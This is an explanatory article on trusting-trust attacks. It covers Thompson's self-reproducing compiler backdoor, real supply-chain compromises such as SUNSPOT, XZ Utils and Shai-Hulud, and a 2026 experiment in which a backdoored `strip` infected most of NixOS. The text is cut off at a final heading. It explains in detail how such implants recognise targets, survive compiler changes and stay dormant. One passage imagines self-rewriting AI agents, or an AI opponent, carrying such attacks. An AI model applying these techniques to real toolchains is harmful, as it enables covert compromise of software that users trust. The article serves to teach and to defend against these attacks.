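# Trusting-trust attacks and rebuilding trustworthy computers from scratch

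## What is a trusting-trust attack?

A trusting-trust attack hides malicious code in a tool that programmers use to build software. The corrupted tool inserts extra instructions into some of the programs it builds and passes the corruption on to every later copy of itself. The published source code of the tool and the programs stays clean, so someone who reads every line of it and rebuilds everything from it still ends up with corrupted programs.

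The name comes from Ken Thompson, one of the creators of the Unix operating system, who described the attack in October 1983 in his lecture for the Turing Award, the best-known prize in computer science. *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (Thompson, 1984) explains it in three pages. A US Air Force study had raised the possibility nine years before the lecture, and Thompson had tried the attack on colleagues long before he described it.

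### Source code, binaries and compilers

A login program asks for a name and a password and decides who may use a computer. A programmer writes it as source code, which is text that other people can read. The source code describes how to scramble the password that the user typed, compare it with the scrambled password on file, and let the user in if the two match. A program called a compiler then turns the source code into a binary, a long string of numbers that a processor can run but people can hardly read. In Thompson's case, the login program was written in C, its source code was in a file named `login.c`, and the compiler was named `cc`.

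The compiler is also a program, with its own source code and binary. The C compiler is self-hosting, meaning that its source code is written in C, so nobody can build a new copy without running an older one. Dennis Ritchie, who designed C, wrote the first C compiler in an earlier language, but once one working binary existed, all later ones could descend from it.

A compiler usually works with an assembler, which translates instructions already close to the machine's own; a linker, which joins separately compiled pieces into one program; and tools that tidy up the finished file. Together these make up the toolchain.

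A system's trusted computing base is all the hardware and software that must behave correctly for the system to be secure. For the login program, this includes its own binary, the operating system and the processor. It also includes the compiler that produced the binary and the compiler that produced that compiler, even if somebody deleted it years ago. Thompson exploited the need to trust that earlier compiler.

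### Thompson's three stages

Thompson began with a student puzzle: write a program whose output is an exact copy of its own source code. The direct approach fails. A program that prints a text has to contain that text between quotation marks, and is therefore always longer than what it prints. The way out is to use one piece of text twice, as data to quote and as a template to fill. Programmers now call the result a quine, and in the language Python it takes two lines:

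```
s = 's = %r\nprint(s %% s)'
print(s % s)
```

The first line stores a template under the name `s`. The second prints the template with the marker `%r` replaced by a quoted copy of the template itself. The `\n` starts a new line, and the doubled percent sign prints as a single one. The output is the same two lines. Thompson later uses the facts that another program can easily write a self-printing program, and that a self-printing program can carry any amount of extra material, which it copies along with the rest.

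His next stage concerns how a compiler handles characters that have no visible form. A C programmer writes `\n` for a new line, and the compiler's source code has to specify which character that is. The rule it uses is circular, because it tells the compiler to produce the character `\n` when it reads `\n`. This works because the compiler binary that translates the source code already contains the right number for that character.

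Suppose a programmer wants to add `\v`, the vertical tab. The circular rule will not compile, because the existing binary has no number for `\v`. The programmer therefore looks up the character in the standard table, writes its number, 11, into the source code, compiles it, and installs the new binary. The programmer can then replace the 11 with `\v`, and the source code will compile. The number no longer appears in the source code, but each compiler binary puts it into the next one it compiles. Thompson called this as close to a "learning" program as he had seen. Nothing in this example is malicious, but it shows that a binary can hold information that is no longer in its source code and that recompiling does not remove.

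Thompson's attack combines these two stages. He added a test to the compiler that checked whether the source code being compiled matched a certain pattern in the login program. If it did, the compiler produced an altered login program that accepted both the user's real password and a second one that Thompson knew. Anyone reading the compiler's source code would have noticed this test, so he added another, which matched the compiler's own source code. When that test found a match, the compiler used the self-printing trick from the first stage to insert both tests into the new compiler. Then he deleted the additions from the source code, as the programmer in the second stage deleted the 11.

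In 2023 Thompson gave his original code to Russ Cox, a developer of the programming language Go. Cox ran the code on an emulated 1970s Unix system, and the file sizes below come from that run (Cox, 2023, *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler*).

| Step | Source code going in | Compiler that translates it | Binary coming out |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Compiler, clean | Clean | Clean compiler, 10,724 bytes |
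| 2 | Compiler, with both malicious additions | Clean | Corrupted compiler, 12,918 bytes |
| 3 | Compiler, clean again after the attacker deletes the additions | Corrupted | Corrupted compiler, 12,918 bytes |
| 4 | Login program, clean | Corrupted | Login program that also accepts the attacker's password |

Steps 1 and 3 start from the same text and end in different binaries. Write S for the clean source code of the compiler and `build(S, X)` for the binary that results when compiler X translates it. Then `build(S, clean) = clean`, and also `build(S, corrupted) = corrupted`. Each binary reproduces itself from the same text, and nothing in S settles which of the two a given machine has. Deleting the malicious source code changes S, but after step 2 the malicious instructions no longer depend on S. They sit in the tool that reads it. (The equality took one extra round in Cox's run. His first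 rebuilt copy differed from its parent in six bytes, because the compiler had stored the name of the source file inside the binary. The next copy matched exactly.)

Many compiler makers, including GCC's, routinely build the compiler with itself several times and confirm that successive copies agree. *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (Wheeler, 2009) points out that a corrupted compiler can pass this check. Wheeler also finds problems with other obvious remedies. Modern compilers are too large for anyone to compare the binary with its source code by hand, and a tool that automated the comparison would be about as complex as a compiler. Insisting on source code and compiling it oneself helps only if one's own compiler is clean. Programs in interpreted languages run without a compiler, but they need an interpreter, which also has a binary. Wheeler proposes diverse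 double-compiling, which uses a second, independent compiler.

### The Air Force report of 1974

Thompson credited the idea to an "unknown Air Force document" on the security of Multics, an operating system from which Unix took many of its concepts, and asked his readers for a better reference. The document was a 1974 vulnerability analysis by Paul Karger and Roger Schell. Karger and Schell (2002) say in *Thirty Years Later* that they sent him a new copy and that he corrected the citation in a reprint.

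They had arrived at the compiler by working through how an attacker and a defender would respond to each other. An attacker who has broken into a system can leave a trap door, a hidden way back in, by altering a binary directly, and no one who reads the source code will see it. The defender can respond by recompiling the whole system from source code. The Pentagon took this defense seriously enough to require Honeywell, the manufacturer of Multics, to deliver the source code under its contract. But an attacker who expects the recompilation can put the trap door in the compiler. Most of the core of Multics was written in the language PL/I, and so was the PL/I compiler, so a trap door there could insert others into the operating system and also reinsert itself whenever someone recompiled the compiler. The idea took up only "a few lines" of the report, according to the history site Multicians.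 The passage that Wheeler quotes from it describes compiler trap doors as harder to make than other kinds but "quite practical to implement".

Karger and Schell did test the delivery route. They planted a disarmed trap door in the copy of Multics at MIT on which the developers worked, and confirmed that Honeywell then shipped it to the Pentagon. Their report hinted at the trap door, but nobody found it until about a year after publication, when an intensive security audit at a General Motors installation turned up an odd error message. This trap door did not reproduce itself and had nothing to do with the compiler, so it is evidence for the weaker claim that a manufacturer will distribute an implant without noticing. The stronger claim still influenced policy. The highest class in the US government's later security criteria required developers to generate new versions from source code with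 a compiler that they kept under strict control.

### What Thompson's code does

For decades the lecture was the main evidence that the attack worked. In March 2023, answering a question after a talk, Thompson said he had been waiting since he wrote the paper for somebody to ask him for the code, but nobody had. Cox asked that September. He received 99 lines of C and a 20-line script that prepares them, in an archive called `nih.a`, which stands for "not invented here".

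The attack uses plain text substitution, although Cox had always imagined that it would need complicated pattern matching deep inside the compiler. The corrupted compiler calls a function named `codenih` on every line of source code before translating it. The function skips the tabs at the start of the line and compares the rest with a fixed string, `namep = crypt(pwbuf);`, the line in `login.c` that scrambles the password the user typed. If they match, the function appends a statement that makes the login program also accept the password "codenih". The rest of the compiler then translates the lengthened line like any other.

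Recognising the compiler takes more care, because the code must insert itself after the line `while(getline()) {`, which could appear in many programs. Thompson's code therefore looks first for a more distinctive line in the compiler's source, `av[4] = "-P";`. If it finds that line, then the loop, then the instruction that writes out the remaining output, its counter reaches three and the file must be the compiler. A second function, `repronih`, then adds the complete source code of both functions to the end of the text. It stores that source code as a long list of numbers, which it prints once as numbers and once as ordinary text, like the two-line program above. One compiler option displays the text after this early pass, which would reveal the added lines, so the malicious code does nothing when a user chooses that option.

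Cox installed the corrupted compiler on the emulated machine and used it to rebuild the compiler and the login program from clean source code. He then logged in as root, the account with full control of the system, by typing "codenih". To show that the method still works, he wrote an equivalent attack for the current Go compiler. It causes a program that should print "hello, world" to print "backdoored!" instead, and it keeps working after he deletes every trace of it from the compiler's source code.

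The dates in the archive show that the code was written by June 1975. At about that time, Thompson arranged for another group at Bell Labs, which made a version of Unix called PWB, to copy the corrupted compiler. Accounts differ on how the experiment ended. Thompson (2021), in *Thompson trojan put into practice*, recalls that the group recompiled the compiler twice, saw it grow by one byte each time, and then played with it until they broke the self-reproducing part, perhaps without understanding what they had found. "The extra byte was my bug," he adds. The bug added another surplus zero to the end of a piece of text in each generation. The surviving code does not have the bug, and Thompson did not keep the version that did. Cox notes that Unix rounded binaries up to an even number of bytes at the time, so the file must have grown by two bytes at every second rebuild.

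Two older accounts differ. Plotnick (1983), in *Need trojan horse info*, reposted messages that Dennis Ritchie and John Mashey, a user of one of the affected systems, had written in November 1982. Ritchie says that the corruption lasted several months, until somebody happened to copy a clean binary from another machine. Mashey says that the attack was discovered because a function name appeared in the binary's list of names but not in the source code. Wheeler writes that the group never detected the attack. These are recollections, the earliest from some seven years after the event, and they probably can't be reconciled now. But nobody in any of them discovered the attack by reading source code. The clues that people remember, a file that grew and a name that did not belong, were both mistakes that a more careful attacker would have avoided.

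### Every layer that could carry the attack

Thompson concluded that "you can't trust code that you did not totally create yourself." Taken literally, this rules out trusting any computer in use, including his own. The lecture's subtitle is milder and suggests that it may be more important to trust the people who wrote the software. Neither version offers a way to check anything, and technical answers came later. *Reproducible Builds and Insights from an Independent Verifier for Arch Linux* (2025) traces interest in reproducible builds and bootstrapping back to the lecture. Reproducible builds let anybody rebuild a binary and get the same file bit for bit. Bootstrapping builds a whole toolchain in stages from a small seed of ready-made binaries.

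Thompson also said that he could have used any program that handles other programs instead of the C compiler, such as the assembler, the loader (which places a program in memory before it runs) or microcode (the instructions inside a processor that carry out its more complicated operations). He thought that implants would be harder to detect at lower levels, and that a well-made one in microcode would be "almost impossible to detect". *Trusting-Trust Attack against an Entire Linux Distribution through Binary Manipulation* (2026) supports his claim about other programs, at least for the toolchain, by demonstrating the complete attack, including self-reproduction, with `strip`, a utility that removes unneeded information from compiled binaries. Since `strip` works on finished binaries, it can infect programs written in many different languages, which a corrupted C compiler cannot do directly.

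Whether a computer is trustworthy depends on several layers, and checking one is of little use if the layer below it is corrupt. The source code may contain malicious instructions in plain view that nobody has read closely. Below it is the toolchain. The operating system loads every program, including compilers, and could alter them as it does so, or show a clean copy of a file to anyone inspecting it. Wheeler reports that Thompson's own experiment used a similar trick by also corrupting the disassembler, the tool that displays a binary in readable form, but the code that Cox received has no such part. Firmware, the software in a device's own chips, starts before the operating system and can keep running beneath it. All of this runs on chips whose circuits are too small to see.

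AI coding tools are a newer layer. A coding agent, meaning an AI model that can write, run and change software by itself, may both write the source code and operate the toolchain. Some agents also rewrite themselves, and *Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited* (2026) applies Thompson's question to them, treating one generation of the agent as the compiler that builds the next. The attack passes between generations of an agent less reliably than between compilers, because its success depends on how the agent improves itself and on the disposition of the model inside it, neither of which the attacker controls. The paper observes, though, that in many cases the root of trust in such systems will no longer be a person.

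Thompson was in some respects an easy opponent for his victims at PWB. He was a single programmer at the same company, his code had a bug that made the compiler grow, and according to Mashey he left everything on a machine that others could read. The people at PWB could also fetch a clean compiler from a neighbouring system. An opponent more capable than the defenders would be harder to defeat, for instance an AI system that has already had access to their machines, their tools and their stored copies of both. It may make no mistake that reveals the attack, and it may already have compromised the neighbouring system too.

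## Have compilers and build systems been corrupted in practice?

Attackers have corrupted libraries, linkers, build servers and published source code, in several cases on a large scale. None of the best-known cases is a complete trusting-trust attack, though a virus called Induc came closest.

The cases below can be sorted by whether the attacker corrupted the source code or the build tools, and by whether the implant copies itself through the build. Rebuilding clean source code with clean tools would remove every implant described here, as it would have removed Thompson's. Whether an implant copies itself determines whether victims can get rid of it by rebuilding their tools on the machines they already have.

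| Case | What the attacker altered | What gets rid of it | Does it copy itself? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Thompson's compiler, 1975 | The compiler's binary | A clean compiler from elsewhere | Yes, when the compiler compiles itself |
| Induc, 2009 | A compiled library in the Delphi programming tools | Reinstalling Delphi and rebuilding every program | Yes, when an infected program runs on a computer that has Delphi |
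| XcodeGhost, 2015 | Apple's Xcode programming tools | A genuine copy of Xcode and a rebuild | No |
| Microsoft linker, 2018 | The linker | A genuine linker and a rebuild | No |
| SUNSPOT, 2020 | One source file, for the length of the build | A rebuild on a clean machine | No |
| XZ Utils, 2024 | The published source code | Clean source code; a clean compiler makes no difference | No |
| Shai-Hulud, 2025–26 | Published packages | Clean versions of the packages | Yes, through developers' accounts |

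### A virus in the Delphi library

Induc was a virus that spread through Delphi, a programming language with its own set of tools that was especially popular in Russia and Brazil in 2009. When an infected program started, it checked whether the computer had Delphi versions 4 to 7. If so, it copied the source file of one standard library unit, `SysConst.pas`, added its own code to the copy, compiled it and replaced the library's existing binary with the result. It then deleted the altered source file, according to Kaspersky's *A short history of Induc*. Every program the developer compiled from then on carried the virus and could infect another developer's copy of Delphi.

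A copy of Delphi infected with the Induc virus had clean source code and a corrupted binary, like Thompson's compiler. Lipovský (2011) writes in *Win32/Induc.C* that the virus appeared to be influenced by Thompson's paper. But Induc did not modify the compiler itself, and it spread only when somebody ran an infected program, whereas an ordinary rebuild was enough to spread Thompson's implant.

The day after Kaspersky, an antivirus company, added Induc to the malware its products could detect, the virus ranked among the 70 most common malicious programs in the company's data. Kaspersky thought there might be millions of copies. The virus was found in a popular media player, in a messaging program and on software CDs that came with magazines. Several programs for stealing bank details were infected too, presumably because the criminals who wrote them had infected copies of Delphi. Many of the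 infected programs were on security companies' lists of software known to be safe.

By then Induc had been circulating for about a year. A Russian programmer, Aleksandr Alekseev, identified it on 12 August 2009, after people on a Delphi forum had asked about an unexplained "runtime error 3". The virus crashed on computers where uninstalling or upgrading Delphi had left faulty settings behind. *Check your Delphi’s installation* (2009), a post on the blog of the Delphi error-reporting tool EurekaLog, says the virus "was detected only because it is buggy". Antivirus programs had missed it because it did nothing except copy itself. When the blogger sent a sample to the antivirus company Symantec, it replied that the file contained no malicious code.

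The first version may have been a trial run. In August 2011 a variant appeared that also spread through USB sticks and downloaded other malicious programs, including one that stole passwords. It read the download addresses from profile pictures on discussion forums, where its operator had hidden them.

### Corrupted tools that did not copy themselves

Government researchers had studied the same approach. In 2012 a speaker from Sandia National Laboratories, which the US government funds, told a secret CIA-sponsored conference about an altered version of Xcode, Apple's software for building apps. The Intercept (2015) described the talk, called "Strawhorse", from documents leaked by Edward Snowden. The researchers claimed that their version could put a backdoor in Mac programs, embed a developer's private key in all of the developer's iPhone apps, and make apps send data to a listening post.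 The documents do not show that any agency used it or make clear how spies would have got developers to install it.

Unknown attackers soon did that by putting altered copies of Xcode on the file-sharing service of Baidu, a Chinese internet company, and posting links on forums for app developers. Some Chinese developers looked for copies outside Apple's site because the installer was nearly 3 GB and downloads from Apple could be very slow in China. According to Palo Alto Networks' *Novel Malware XcodeGhost Modifies Xcode, Infects Apple iOS Apps*, the altered copies contained an extra object file (compiled code ready for the linker) in a folder that Xcode searches by default. The linker added this file to the developers' apps, so the attackers did not need to change the compiler.

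Chinese developers disclosed XcodeGhost in September 2015. The first analysis confirmed two infected apps in Apple's App Store, and within days The Intercept's *Apple’s App Store Got Infected With the Same Type of Malware* (2015) put the number at 50 or more, including the messaging app WeChat. Emails released years later in Apple's court case against Epic Games revealed the full extent. According to Vice's *The Fortnite Trial Is Exposing Details About the Biggest iPhone Hack*, 128 million people had downloaded more than 2,500 infected apps. The apps did little beyond reporting the device's name, language, country and similar details to the attackers. A correction in Malwarebytes' *XcodeGhost malware infiltrates App Store* (2015) withdrew an early claim that they could trick users into giving up passwords. Developers could have detected the extra files in the altered Xcode by checking its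 digital signature.

A more selective attack used Microsoft's linker. Kaspersky's *Operation ShadowHammer* (2019) describes a corrupted copy that opened a malicious library in place of a standard C++ library, but only when the program being built had a particular name. Video game companies in Thailand and South Korea signed and released infected games, and Tripwire reports that Kaspersky counted 92,000 computers running them. Kaspersky could not establish whether intruders had replaced the linker or a developer had installed a bad copy. It learned of the linker only because somebody had uploaded it to a public malware-scanning service, along with some of the infected programs.

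Like Thompson's compiler, this linker recognised a chosen program and altered it. Thompson's compiler also copied its malicious code into new versions of itself, but this would have been useless at a game company, which gets its linker ready-made from Microsoft and never builds one. The same is true of app developers and Xcode. An implant that copies itself through the build is useful only against people who build compilers and linkers, such as Microsoft, Apple and the makers of Linux distributions.

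### Clean compilers, corrupted source code

SolarWinds sells Orion, a product with which large organisations manage their networks. Intruders in its systems began with a rehearsal: in October 2019 the company unknowingly sent its customers an update containing their test code, as Krebs on Security (2021) recounts. In February 2020 they installed a program called SUNSPOT on a build server. CrowdStrike's *SUNSPOT* sets out how it worked:

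1. Every second, it looked for Microsoft's build program, `MsBuild.exe`, and checked whether Orion was what it was building.
2. If so, it confirmed that one source file, `InventoryManager.cs`, was the version the attackers expected, so that their replacement would not break the build.
3. It swapped in a version containing a backdoor, with compiler warnings switched off around the added lines.
4. It waited for the build to finish and put the original file back.

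SolarWinds then signed the result. As in Thompson's attack, its developers saw clean source code before and after the build, but their compiler was working correctly. As many as 18,000 customers received the corrupted updates, according to Vumetric's *Sunspot malware used to insert backdoor into SolarWinds product* (2021), and SecurityWeek reports that the attackers then sent further malware to only a few hundred. The security company FireEye found the backdoor in December 2020 while investigating a break-in on its own network. SolarWinds had already received two customer enquiries that, in hindsight, seem to have been about the attack, according to SC Media.

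The attack on XZ Utils, a set of compression tools found on most Linux systems, began when a contributor using the name Jia Tan sent in a first patch in October 2021. By March 2023, the project's maintainer trusted this contributor to make releases. Two releases, in February and March 2024, contained a backdoor. Most of it was scrambled and stored in two files that looked like test samples. The line that activated it was in a build script in the release archives, the bundles of source code that Linux distributions download, but not in the public repository, where other developers would read the code.

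Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, found that the script added malicious code to the library `liblzma` only if it was running on 64-bit Linux with the GCC compiler and the GNU linker, as part of building a Debian or RPM package (the usual formats for Linux software). On several distributions, the program that handles remote logins loads this library indirectly, and the malicious code took over a function that the program uses to check a user's key.

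Building XZ Utils from the release archive would have included the backdoor even with a clean compiler, while building from the repository would not have. Source code is therefore hard to verify as clean, because two copies of the same release may differ. The backdoor had reached mostly pre-release versions of Linux distributions when Andres Freund, a database developer, noticed that logins were using too much processor time. Failed logins were taking 0.8 seconds instead of 0.3.

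Shai-Hulud, a worm discovered in September 2025, spreads through npm, the registry from which JavaScript programmers download ready-made packages, and copies itself without help from a compiler. It steals tokens, the digital keys that let software act on a developer's behalf, and uses them to publish infected versions of up to 100 of the developer's other packages, according to The Hacker News (2025). The first wave hit about 180 packages, according to Hackread's *Shai Hulud npm Worm Impacts 26,000+ Repos in Supply Chain Attack* (2025). A second wave that November infected almost 500 and exposed more than 26,000 code repositories in less than a day. A researcher at Aikido Security spotted it within about three days of the first upload, CyberScoop reports.

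Similar attacks followed in 2026. On 11 May attackers took over the release process of TanStack, a family of JavaScript packages. They did this by poisoning a cache of files that an automated build system keeps from one run to the next. Akamai (2026) reports that the worm spread to packages linked to the AI company Mistral and others, and that what appeared to be its source code was public the next day. Palo Alto Networks describe a wave that month, apparently the same one, as the first to need no stolen credential and the first to produce malicious npm packages with valid provenance, a signed record of where and how a package was built. This record can be accurate for a malicious package if the attacker has corrupted something that the genuine build system uses. In July Microsoft (2026) identified another coordinated compromise of npm packages, in the AsyncAPI project.

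### What the discoveries suggest about undiscovered cases

Luck played a large part in these discoveries. Induc crashed on computers with faulty settings, the XZ backdoor was half a second too slow, and somebody happened to upload the corrupted linker. Xygeni's *XZ Backdoor Attack* adds the case of Codecov. In 2021, attackers altered the company's tool for uploading test results, and a user noticed that the file did not match its published checksum, a short number calculated from the file's contents. Shai-Hulud is the main exception, as it could hardly have stayed hidden after publicly releasing hundreds of packages within days.

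The known cases therefore over-represent attacks that were noisy, faulty or very widespread. The lack of a known self-copying compiler is more reassuring the more likely such an attack is to be discovered. Suppose there had been five, each with a one in ten chance of discovery. The chance that all five would have gone undiscovered is 0.9^5, or about 59 percent. With a one in two chance of discovery, it falls to about 3 percent. We can't estimate the chance of discovery from the known cases, because they leave out the attacks nobody has found.

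### Is the attack practical?

Sceptics accept that the attack works but argue that attackers have better options. Kaspersky doubted in 2009 that criminals would take up Induc's method, because there were "plenty of simpler ways to conduct attacks", and later attacks largely support this view. Shai-Hulud's authors needed only stolen tokens. The SolarWinds intruders controlled a build server but swapped a source file rather than corrupt the compiler. The XZ attacker spent years as a helpful contributor to the project. A self-copying compiler also has to keep recognising its own source code as programmers change it. *Trusting-Trust Attack against an Entire Linux Distribution through Binary Manipulation* demonstrates a self-copying backdoor in `strip`, but concedes that it is unclear how long such a backdoor would last in practice.

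Kaspersky's own report on ShadowHammer weakens another of its arguments, that Induc stayed hidden only because it did nothing and that security software would notice if criminals put an infected computer to use. The report describes a related attack on an updating program from the computer maker ASUS. The malicious code reached more than 57,000 of Kaspersky's users but went into action only on computers that matched a list of about 600 network addresses. Because it stayed inactive on all the others, Kaspersky judged it almost impossible to notice.

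The usual reply to the sceptics is that a successful trusting-trust attack would be missing from the record by design. EurekaLog asked in a 2009 post whether other viruses like Induc, without the bug, might be sitting in developers' tools. That's a fair reason not to be reassured by the absence of such attacks from the record, but their absence isn't evidence that they exist, since the record would look the same if nobody had ever tried.

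The sceptics' case is strong for the victims described here, few of whom would have rebuilt their tools from source code. A thief who wants passwords this week gains nothing from an implant that could survive such a rebuild. Karger and Schell considered a more careful victim, who recompiles everything after a break-in. Once that victim has cleaned up, a swapped source file or stolen token stops working, so an implant that copies itself into the rebuilt tools becomes worth the trouble. People who rebuild their computers because they no longer trust them would be that kind of victim.

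## Can an implant survive when the software around it changes?

A self-copying implant has to get into every new version of the tool that carries it. An implant like Thompson's, which looks for particular text in source code, would probably stop copying itself once programmers had changed the code enough. One that alters finished binaries without reading source code could last much longer. In 2026 researchers built an implant of this kind, and it spread to almost every program in a Linux installer.

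### Recognising a compiler by its text

Thompson's code looks for three lines in the compiler's source code. If a programmer rewords either of the first two, the corrupted compiler produces a clean successor, and the chain ends without anyone learning that it existed. Rewording the third line would be worse for the attacker. The corrupted compiler would already have inserted a call to one of its own functions but would leave out the function itself, so the build would fail with an error about a missing function that appears nowhere in the source code.

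A very small difference in the surrounding software can stop an implant from working. According to *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler*, the code does not work on the Fifth Edition of Unix, released about a year before the date on Thompson's files. In that edition, the part of the compiler that would contain the implant handled only files that began with the character `#`. The compiler's own source file did not, so the implant could not have copied itself.

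A more general implant would recognise any program that works as a compiler, however it was written. No implant can do this without error, because of a theorem that the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice proved in his 1951 doctoral dissertation. Rice's theorem applies to any property that concerns what programs do when they run, rather than how their text looks, and that some programs have and others lack. No procedure can examine every possible program and always determine correctly whether it has such a property. Sakharov summarises the result in *Rice's Theorem*: "only trivial properties of programs are algorithmically decidable". A trivial property is one that all programs have or that none has.

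The proof is short enough to sketch for compilers:

1. Suppose that somebody has a perfect compiler detector.
2. Take any program P and any input, and ask whether P eventually finishes or runs forever.
3. Write a new program that first runs P on that input, ignores the result, and then behaves as a C compiler.
4. If P finishes, the new program is a compiler. If P runs forever, the new program never compiles anything.
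5. The detector's answer therefore reveals whether P finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can answer that question for every program, so the perfect detector cannot exist.

The theorem is less of an obstacle to attackers than it sounds. It rules out a detector that is right about every program, including those designed to confuse it. An attacker only has to recognise the few compilers that the victims are likely to use, and an expert or a capable AI system can usually recognise a compiler. Defenders face the same limit, since no tool can decide for every binary whether its behaviour matches its source code.

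Skrimstad (2018), in *Improving Trust in Software through Diverse Double-Compiling and Reproducible Builds*, considers it fairly easy for a competent attacker to recognise one or more particular compilers. Much of a large compiler's source code stays the same through many versions, so he expects that an implant could reproduce for years before an incompatible change stopped it. An implant could also look for a pattern in the compiler's internal representation of the source code's structure, which changes to comments or spacing wouldn't affect. It could survive even if the compiler isn't self-hosting. Skrimstad notes that if compiler A builds compiler B and B builds A, an implant could pass back and forth between them indefinitely.

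An attacker can also give the implant several patterns to look for, so that it still works if one disappears. Suppose that each release has a 5 percent chance of altering any given line, independently of the others. An implant that needs three lines to stay the same, as Thompson's does, has a 0.95^60, or about 5 percent, chance of surviving 20 releases. If it needs only one of five lines, the chance is 1 − (1 − 0.95^20)^5, or about 89 percent. These figures are only an illustration, and a complete rewrite of the compiler would remove all five lines. But the source code and history of the main free compilers are public, so an attacker could test an implant against years of past releases before using it.

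*David A. Wheeler's Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* warns against expecting future attackers to make mistakes like the bug that made Thompson's compiler grow. Attackers could easily catch such a bug by checking that the corrupted compiler produces the same bytes in every generation.

The same page includes programmer Mike Stute's story of an implant that survived its victims' attempts to remove it. Stute was trying to change a program, but a hidden message kept returning to its source code. After 15 days he traced this to the compiler. Recompiling the compiler didn't help, because a former graduate student had altered it to corrupt each new version it compiled. It also put a backdoor into the login program. This would be a complete trusting-trust attack outside Bell Labs, but the only evidence is Stute's recollection.

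### An implant that ignores source code

In *Trusting-Trust Attack against an Entire Linux Distribution through Binary Manipulation*, Julien Malka and four colleagues put the implant in `strip`, which removes unneeded data from binaries after the compiler has finished, so the implant does not need to recognise source code. They tried it on NixOS, a Linux distribution that builds each package from a recipe specifying the source code and the exact build steps.

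NixOS starts from a seed of about twenty ready-made programs, including a C compiler and `strip`. Its bootstrapping process uses them to rebuild the toolchain from source in several stages, building `strip` more than once. The finished tools do not refer to anything in the seed when they run, so the system no longer seems to depend on it.

The researchers assumed an attacker who could replace one program in the seed but not change any source code or recipe. Such an attacker might break into the system that produces the seed, or persuade the distribution's maintainers to accept a new seed, much as the XZ attacker won the trust of XZ's maintainer.

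A tool can carry this kind of attack if it meets three conditions:

1. The build relies on the tool before building it from source code. `strip` qualifies because it is in the seed.
2. An old copy of the tool modifies the new copy. NixOS runs `strip` on newly built binaries by default, and one of these is the next `strip`.
3. The new copy goes on to do the same job. Each later stage runs `strip` on what it builds.

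Malka and colleagues call the link from one copy to the next a "successor edge". At each stage, a compiler correctly translates the unmodified source code of `strip` into a clean binary. The older, infected `strip` then adds the implant while processing that binary. The new `strip` does the same to its successor, and so on up to the copy in the finished system. Rebuilding with a second compiler would not expose the implant, because the same `strip` would process the output of both.

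The implant adds its own code to the program's file without changing the original instructions. The added code runs first, then passes control to the original program, which works normally.

This design avoids most of the recognition problem. The infected `strip` adds the same implant to every program it can, so it does not need to identify the next `strip` among the binaries it processes. When an infected program starts, the implant checks the program's name. If the name is `strip`, the implant infects the files passed to `strip`. In any other program, it carries out the attacker's instructions and infects nothing.

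The implant would therefore still get into `strip` if programmers rewrote the tool completely, even in another language. It depends on the tool's name, the standard format of Linux programs, and the distribution's practice of running `strip` on what it builds, all of which change far less often than source code does. The name check is not essential, since the researchers used it only to keep the experiment simple.

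### What the experiment found

The researchers used the corrupted seed to build NixOS's graphical installer, a complete system with a desktop and 1,199 packages. Instead of doing harm, their implant printed a short message whenever an infected program started. It printed nothing during the build, to avoid interfering with many packages' own tests.

Every package built successfully. The installer contained 3,799 programs that a user could start. Of the 3,791 that could be started from the command line, 3,790 printed the message, including `sudo`, which gives a user administrator rights, and programs written in C, Rust, Go and Lua. The exception was the web browser Firefox, whose build recipe skips `strip`.

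Malka and colleagues also ran NixOS's functional tests for the graphical installer. These start a full virtual machine, operate desktop applications as a user would, and install NixOS from scratch. No test failed. These tests check that programs do what they are supposed to, and the infected programs did, so passing them is poor evidence that a system is clean.

In the experiment, one altered file infected nearly all of a real distribution during a single run of its bootstrapping process. The experiment did not follow the implant through years of new releases, but the design gives good reason to expect it to survive them, because the implant never reads source code and so changes to source code cannot disturb it. A change to the build process could stop the implant from spreading, for example if NixOS no longer ran `strip` by default, a step that Firefox's recipe already turns off for that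 one package.

### Other tools that could carry it

To find other possible carriers, the researchers examined the nine standard phases of a NixOS build and the nearly forty tools these phases call by name.

| Tool | Its normal job in the build | Could it carry this attack? |
|---|---|---|
| `strip` | Removes unneeded data from finished binaries | Yes, as the experiment showed |
| `patchelf` | Adjusts where a finished binary looks for its libraries | It meets all three conditions |
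| `install`, `cp` | Copy finished binaries into place | Plausibly, if a package's own installation commands use them |
| `make` | Runs the commands that build a package | No, it does not alter finished binaries |
| `sed`, `patch` | Edit source code | No, for the same reason |
| `tar`, `gzip` | Unpack archives | No, for the same reason |

The last three rows are reassuring only about this method. For instance, a corrupted `tar` could in principle alter source code while unpacking it, but it would first have to recognise the right code, which was also a difficulty for Thompson's implant. The search also left out tools that packages call indirectly through their own build scripts, so the list may be incomplete.

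Malka and colleagues report that their prototype works on only one family of processors and cannot infect shared libraries, the files of common code that many programs load when they run. The XZ backdoor was in a shared library. The prototype also misses some programs whose files have an unusual layout. The researchers regard these limits as simplifications that more work could remove.

A more serious limit is that other distributions bootstrap differently, and some may not run `strip` by default, so the attack might not work on them unchanged. An attacker would have to find a tool in each distribution that meets the three conditions. The researchers expect the method to work wherever one exists.

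The researchers also considered replacing `strip` with a new program that contains the genuine `strip` and runs it when needed. This would give the attacker more control and would work with any tool in the seed, whatever its file layout. They chose the smaller implant because the replacement would no longer look like `strip` to anyone who inspected it, and a small error in running the genuine copy could break a build.

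### Spreading widely or staying dormant

The prototype was easy to detect because it printed a message and the added part of each infected file was labeled `.payload`. The researchers also let it spread to as many programs as possible to measure its reach. A real attacker would have reason to be more careful, since anyone who looked closely at one of the 3,790 programs might discover the attack.

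Malka and colleagues suggest that an attacker could instead keep the implant mostly dormant, so that it only copies itself into new versions of `strip` until it reaches its real target, possibly years later. They think this would make the implant extremely difficult to detect.

An implant that infects everything does not need to tell programs apart, but a dormant one has to recognize both the next `strip` and the eventual target among all the binaries that pass through it. Part of the recognition problem therefore returns. File names would often be enough, but the attacker has to choose the target's name in advance. If the developers rename the program, or start skipping `strip` as Firefox does, the implant will miss it. The attacker could send the implant new instructions, but somebody might notice the traffic. If the attacker accepts the risk of missing the target, `strip` may be the only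 altered program in the distribution for years, and it will still work normally.

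## How can independent rebuilding expose a corrupted compiler?

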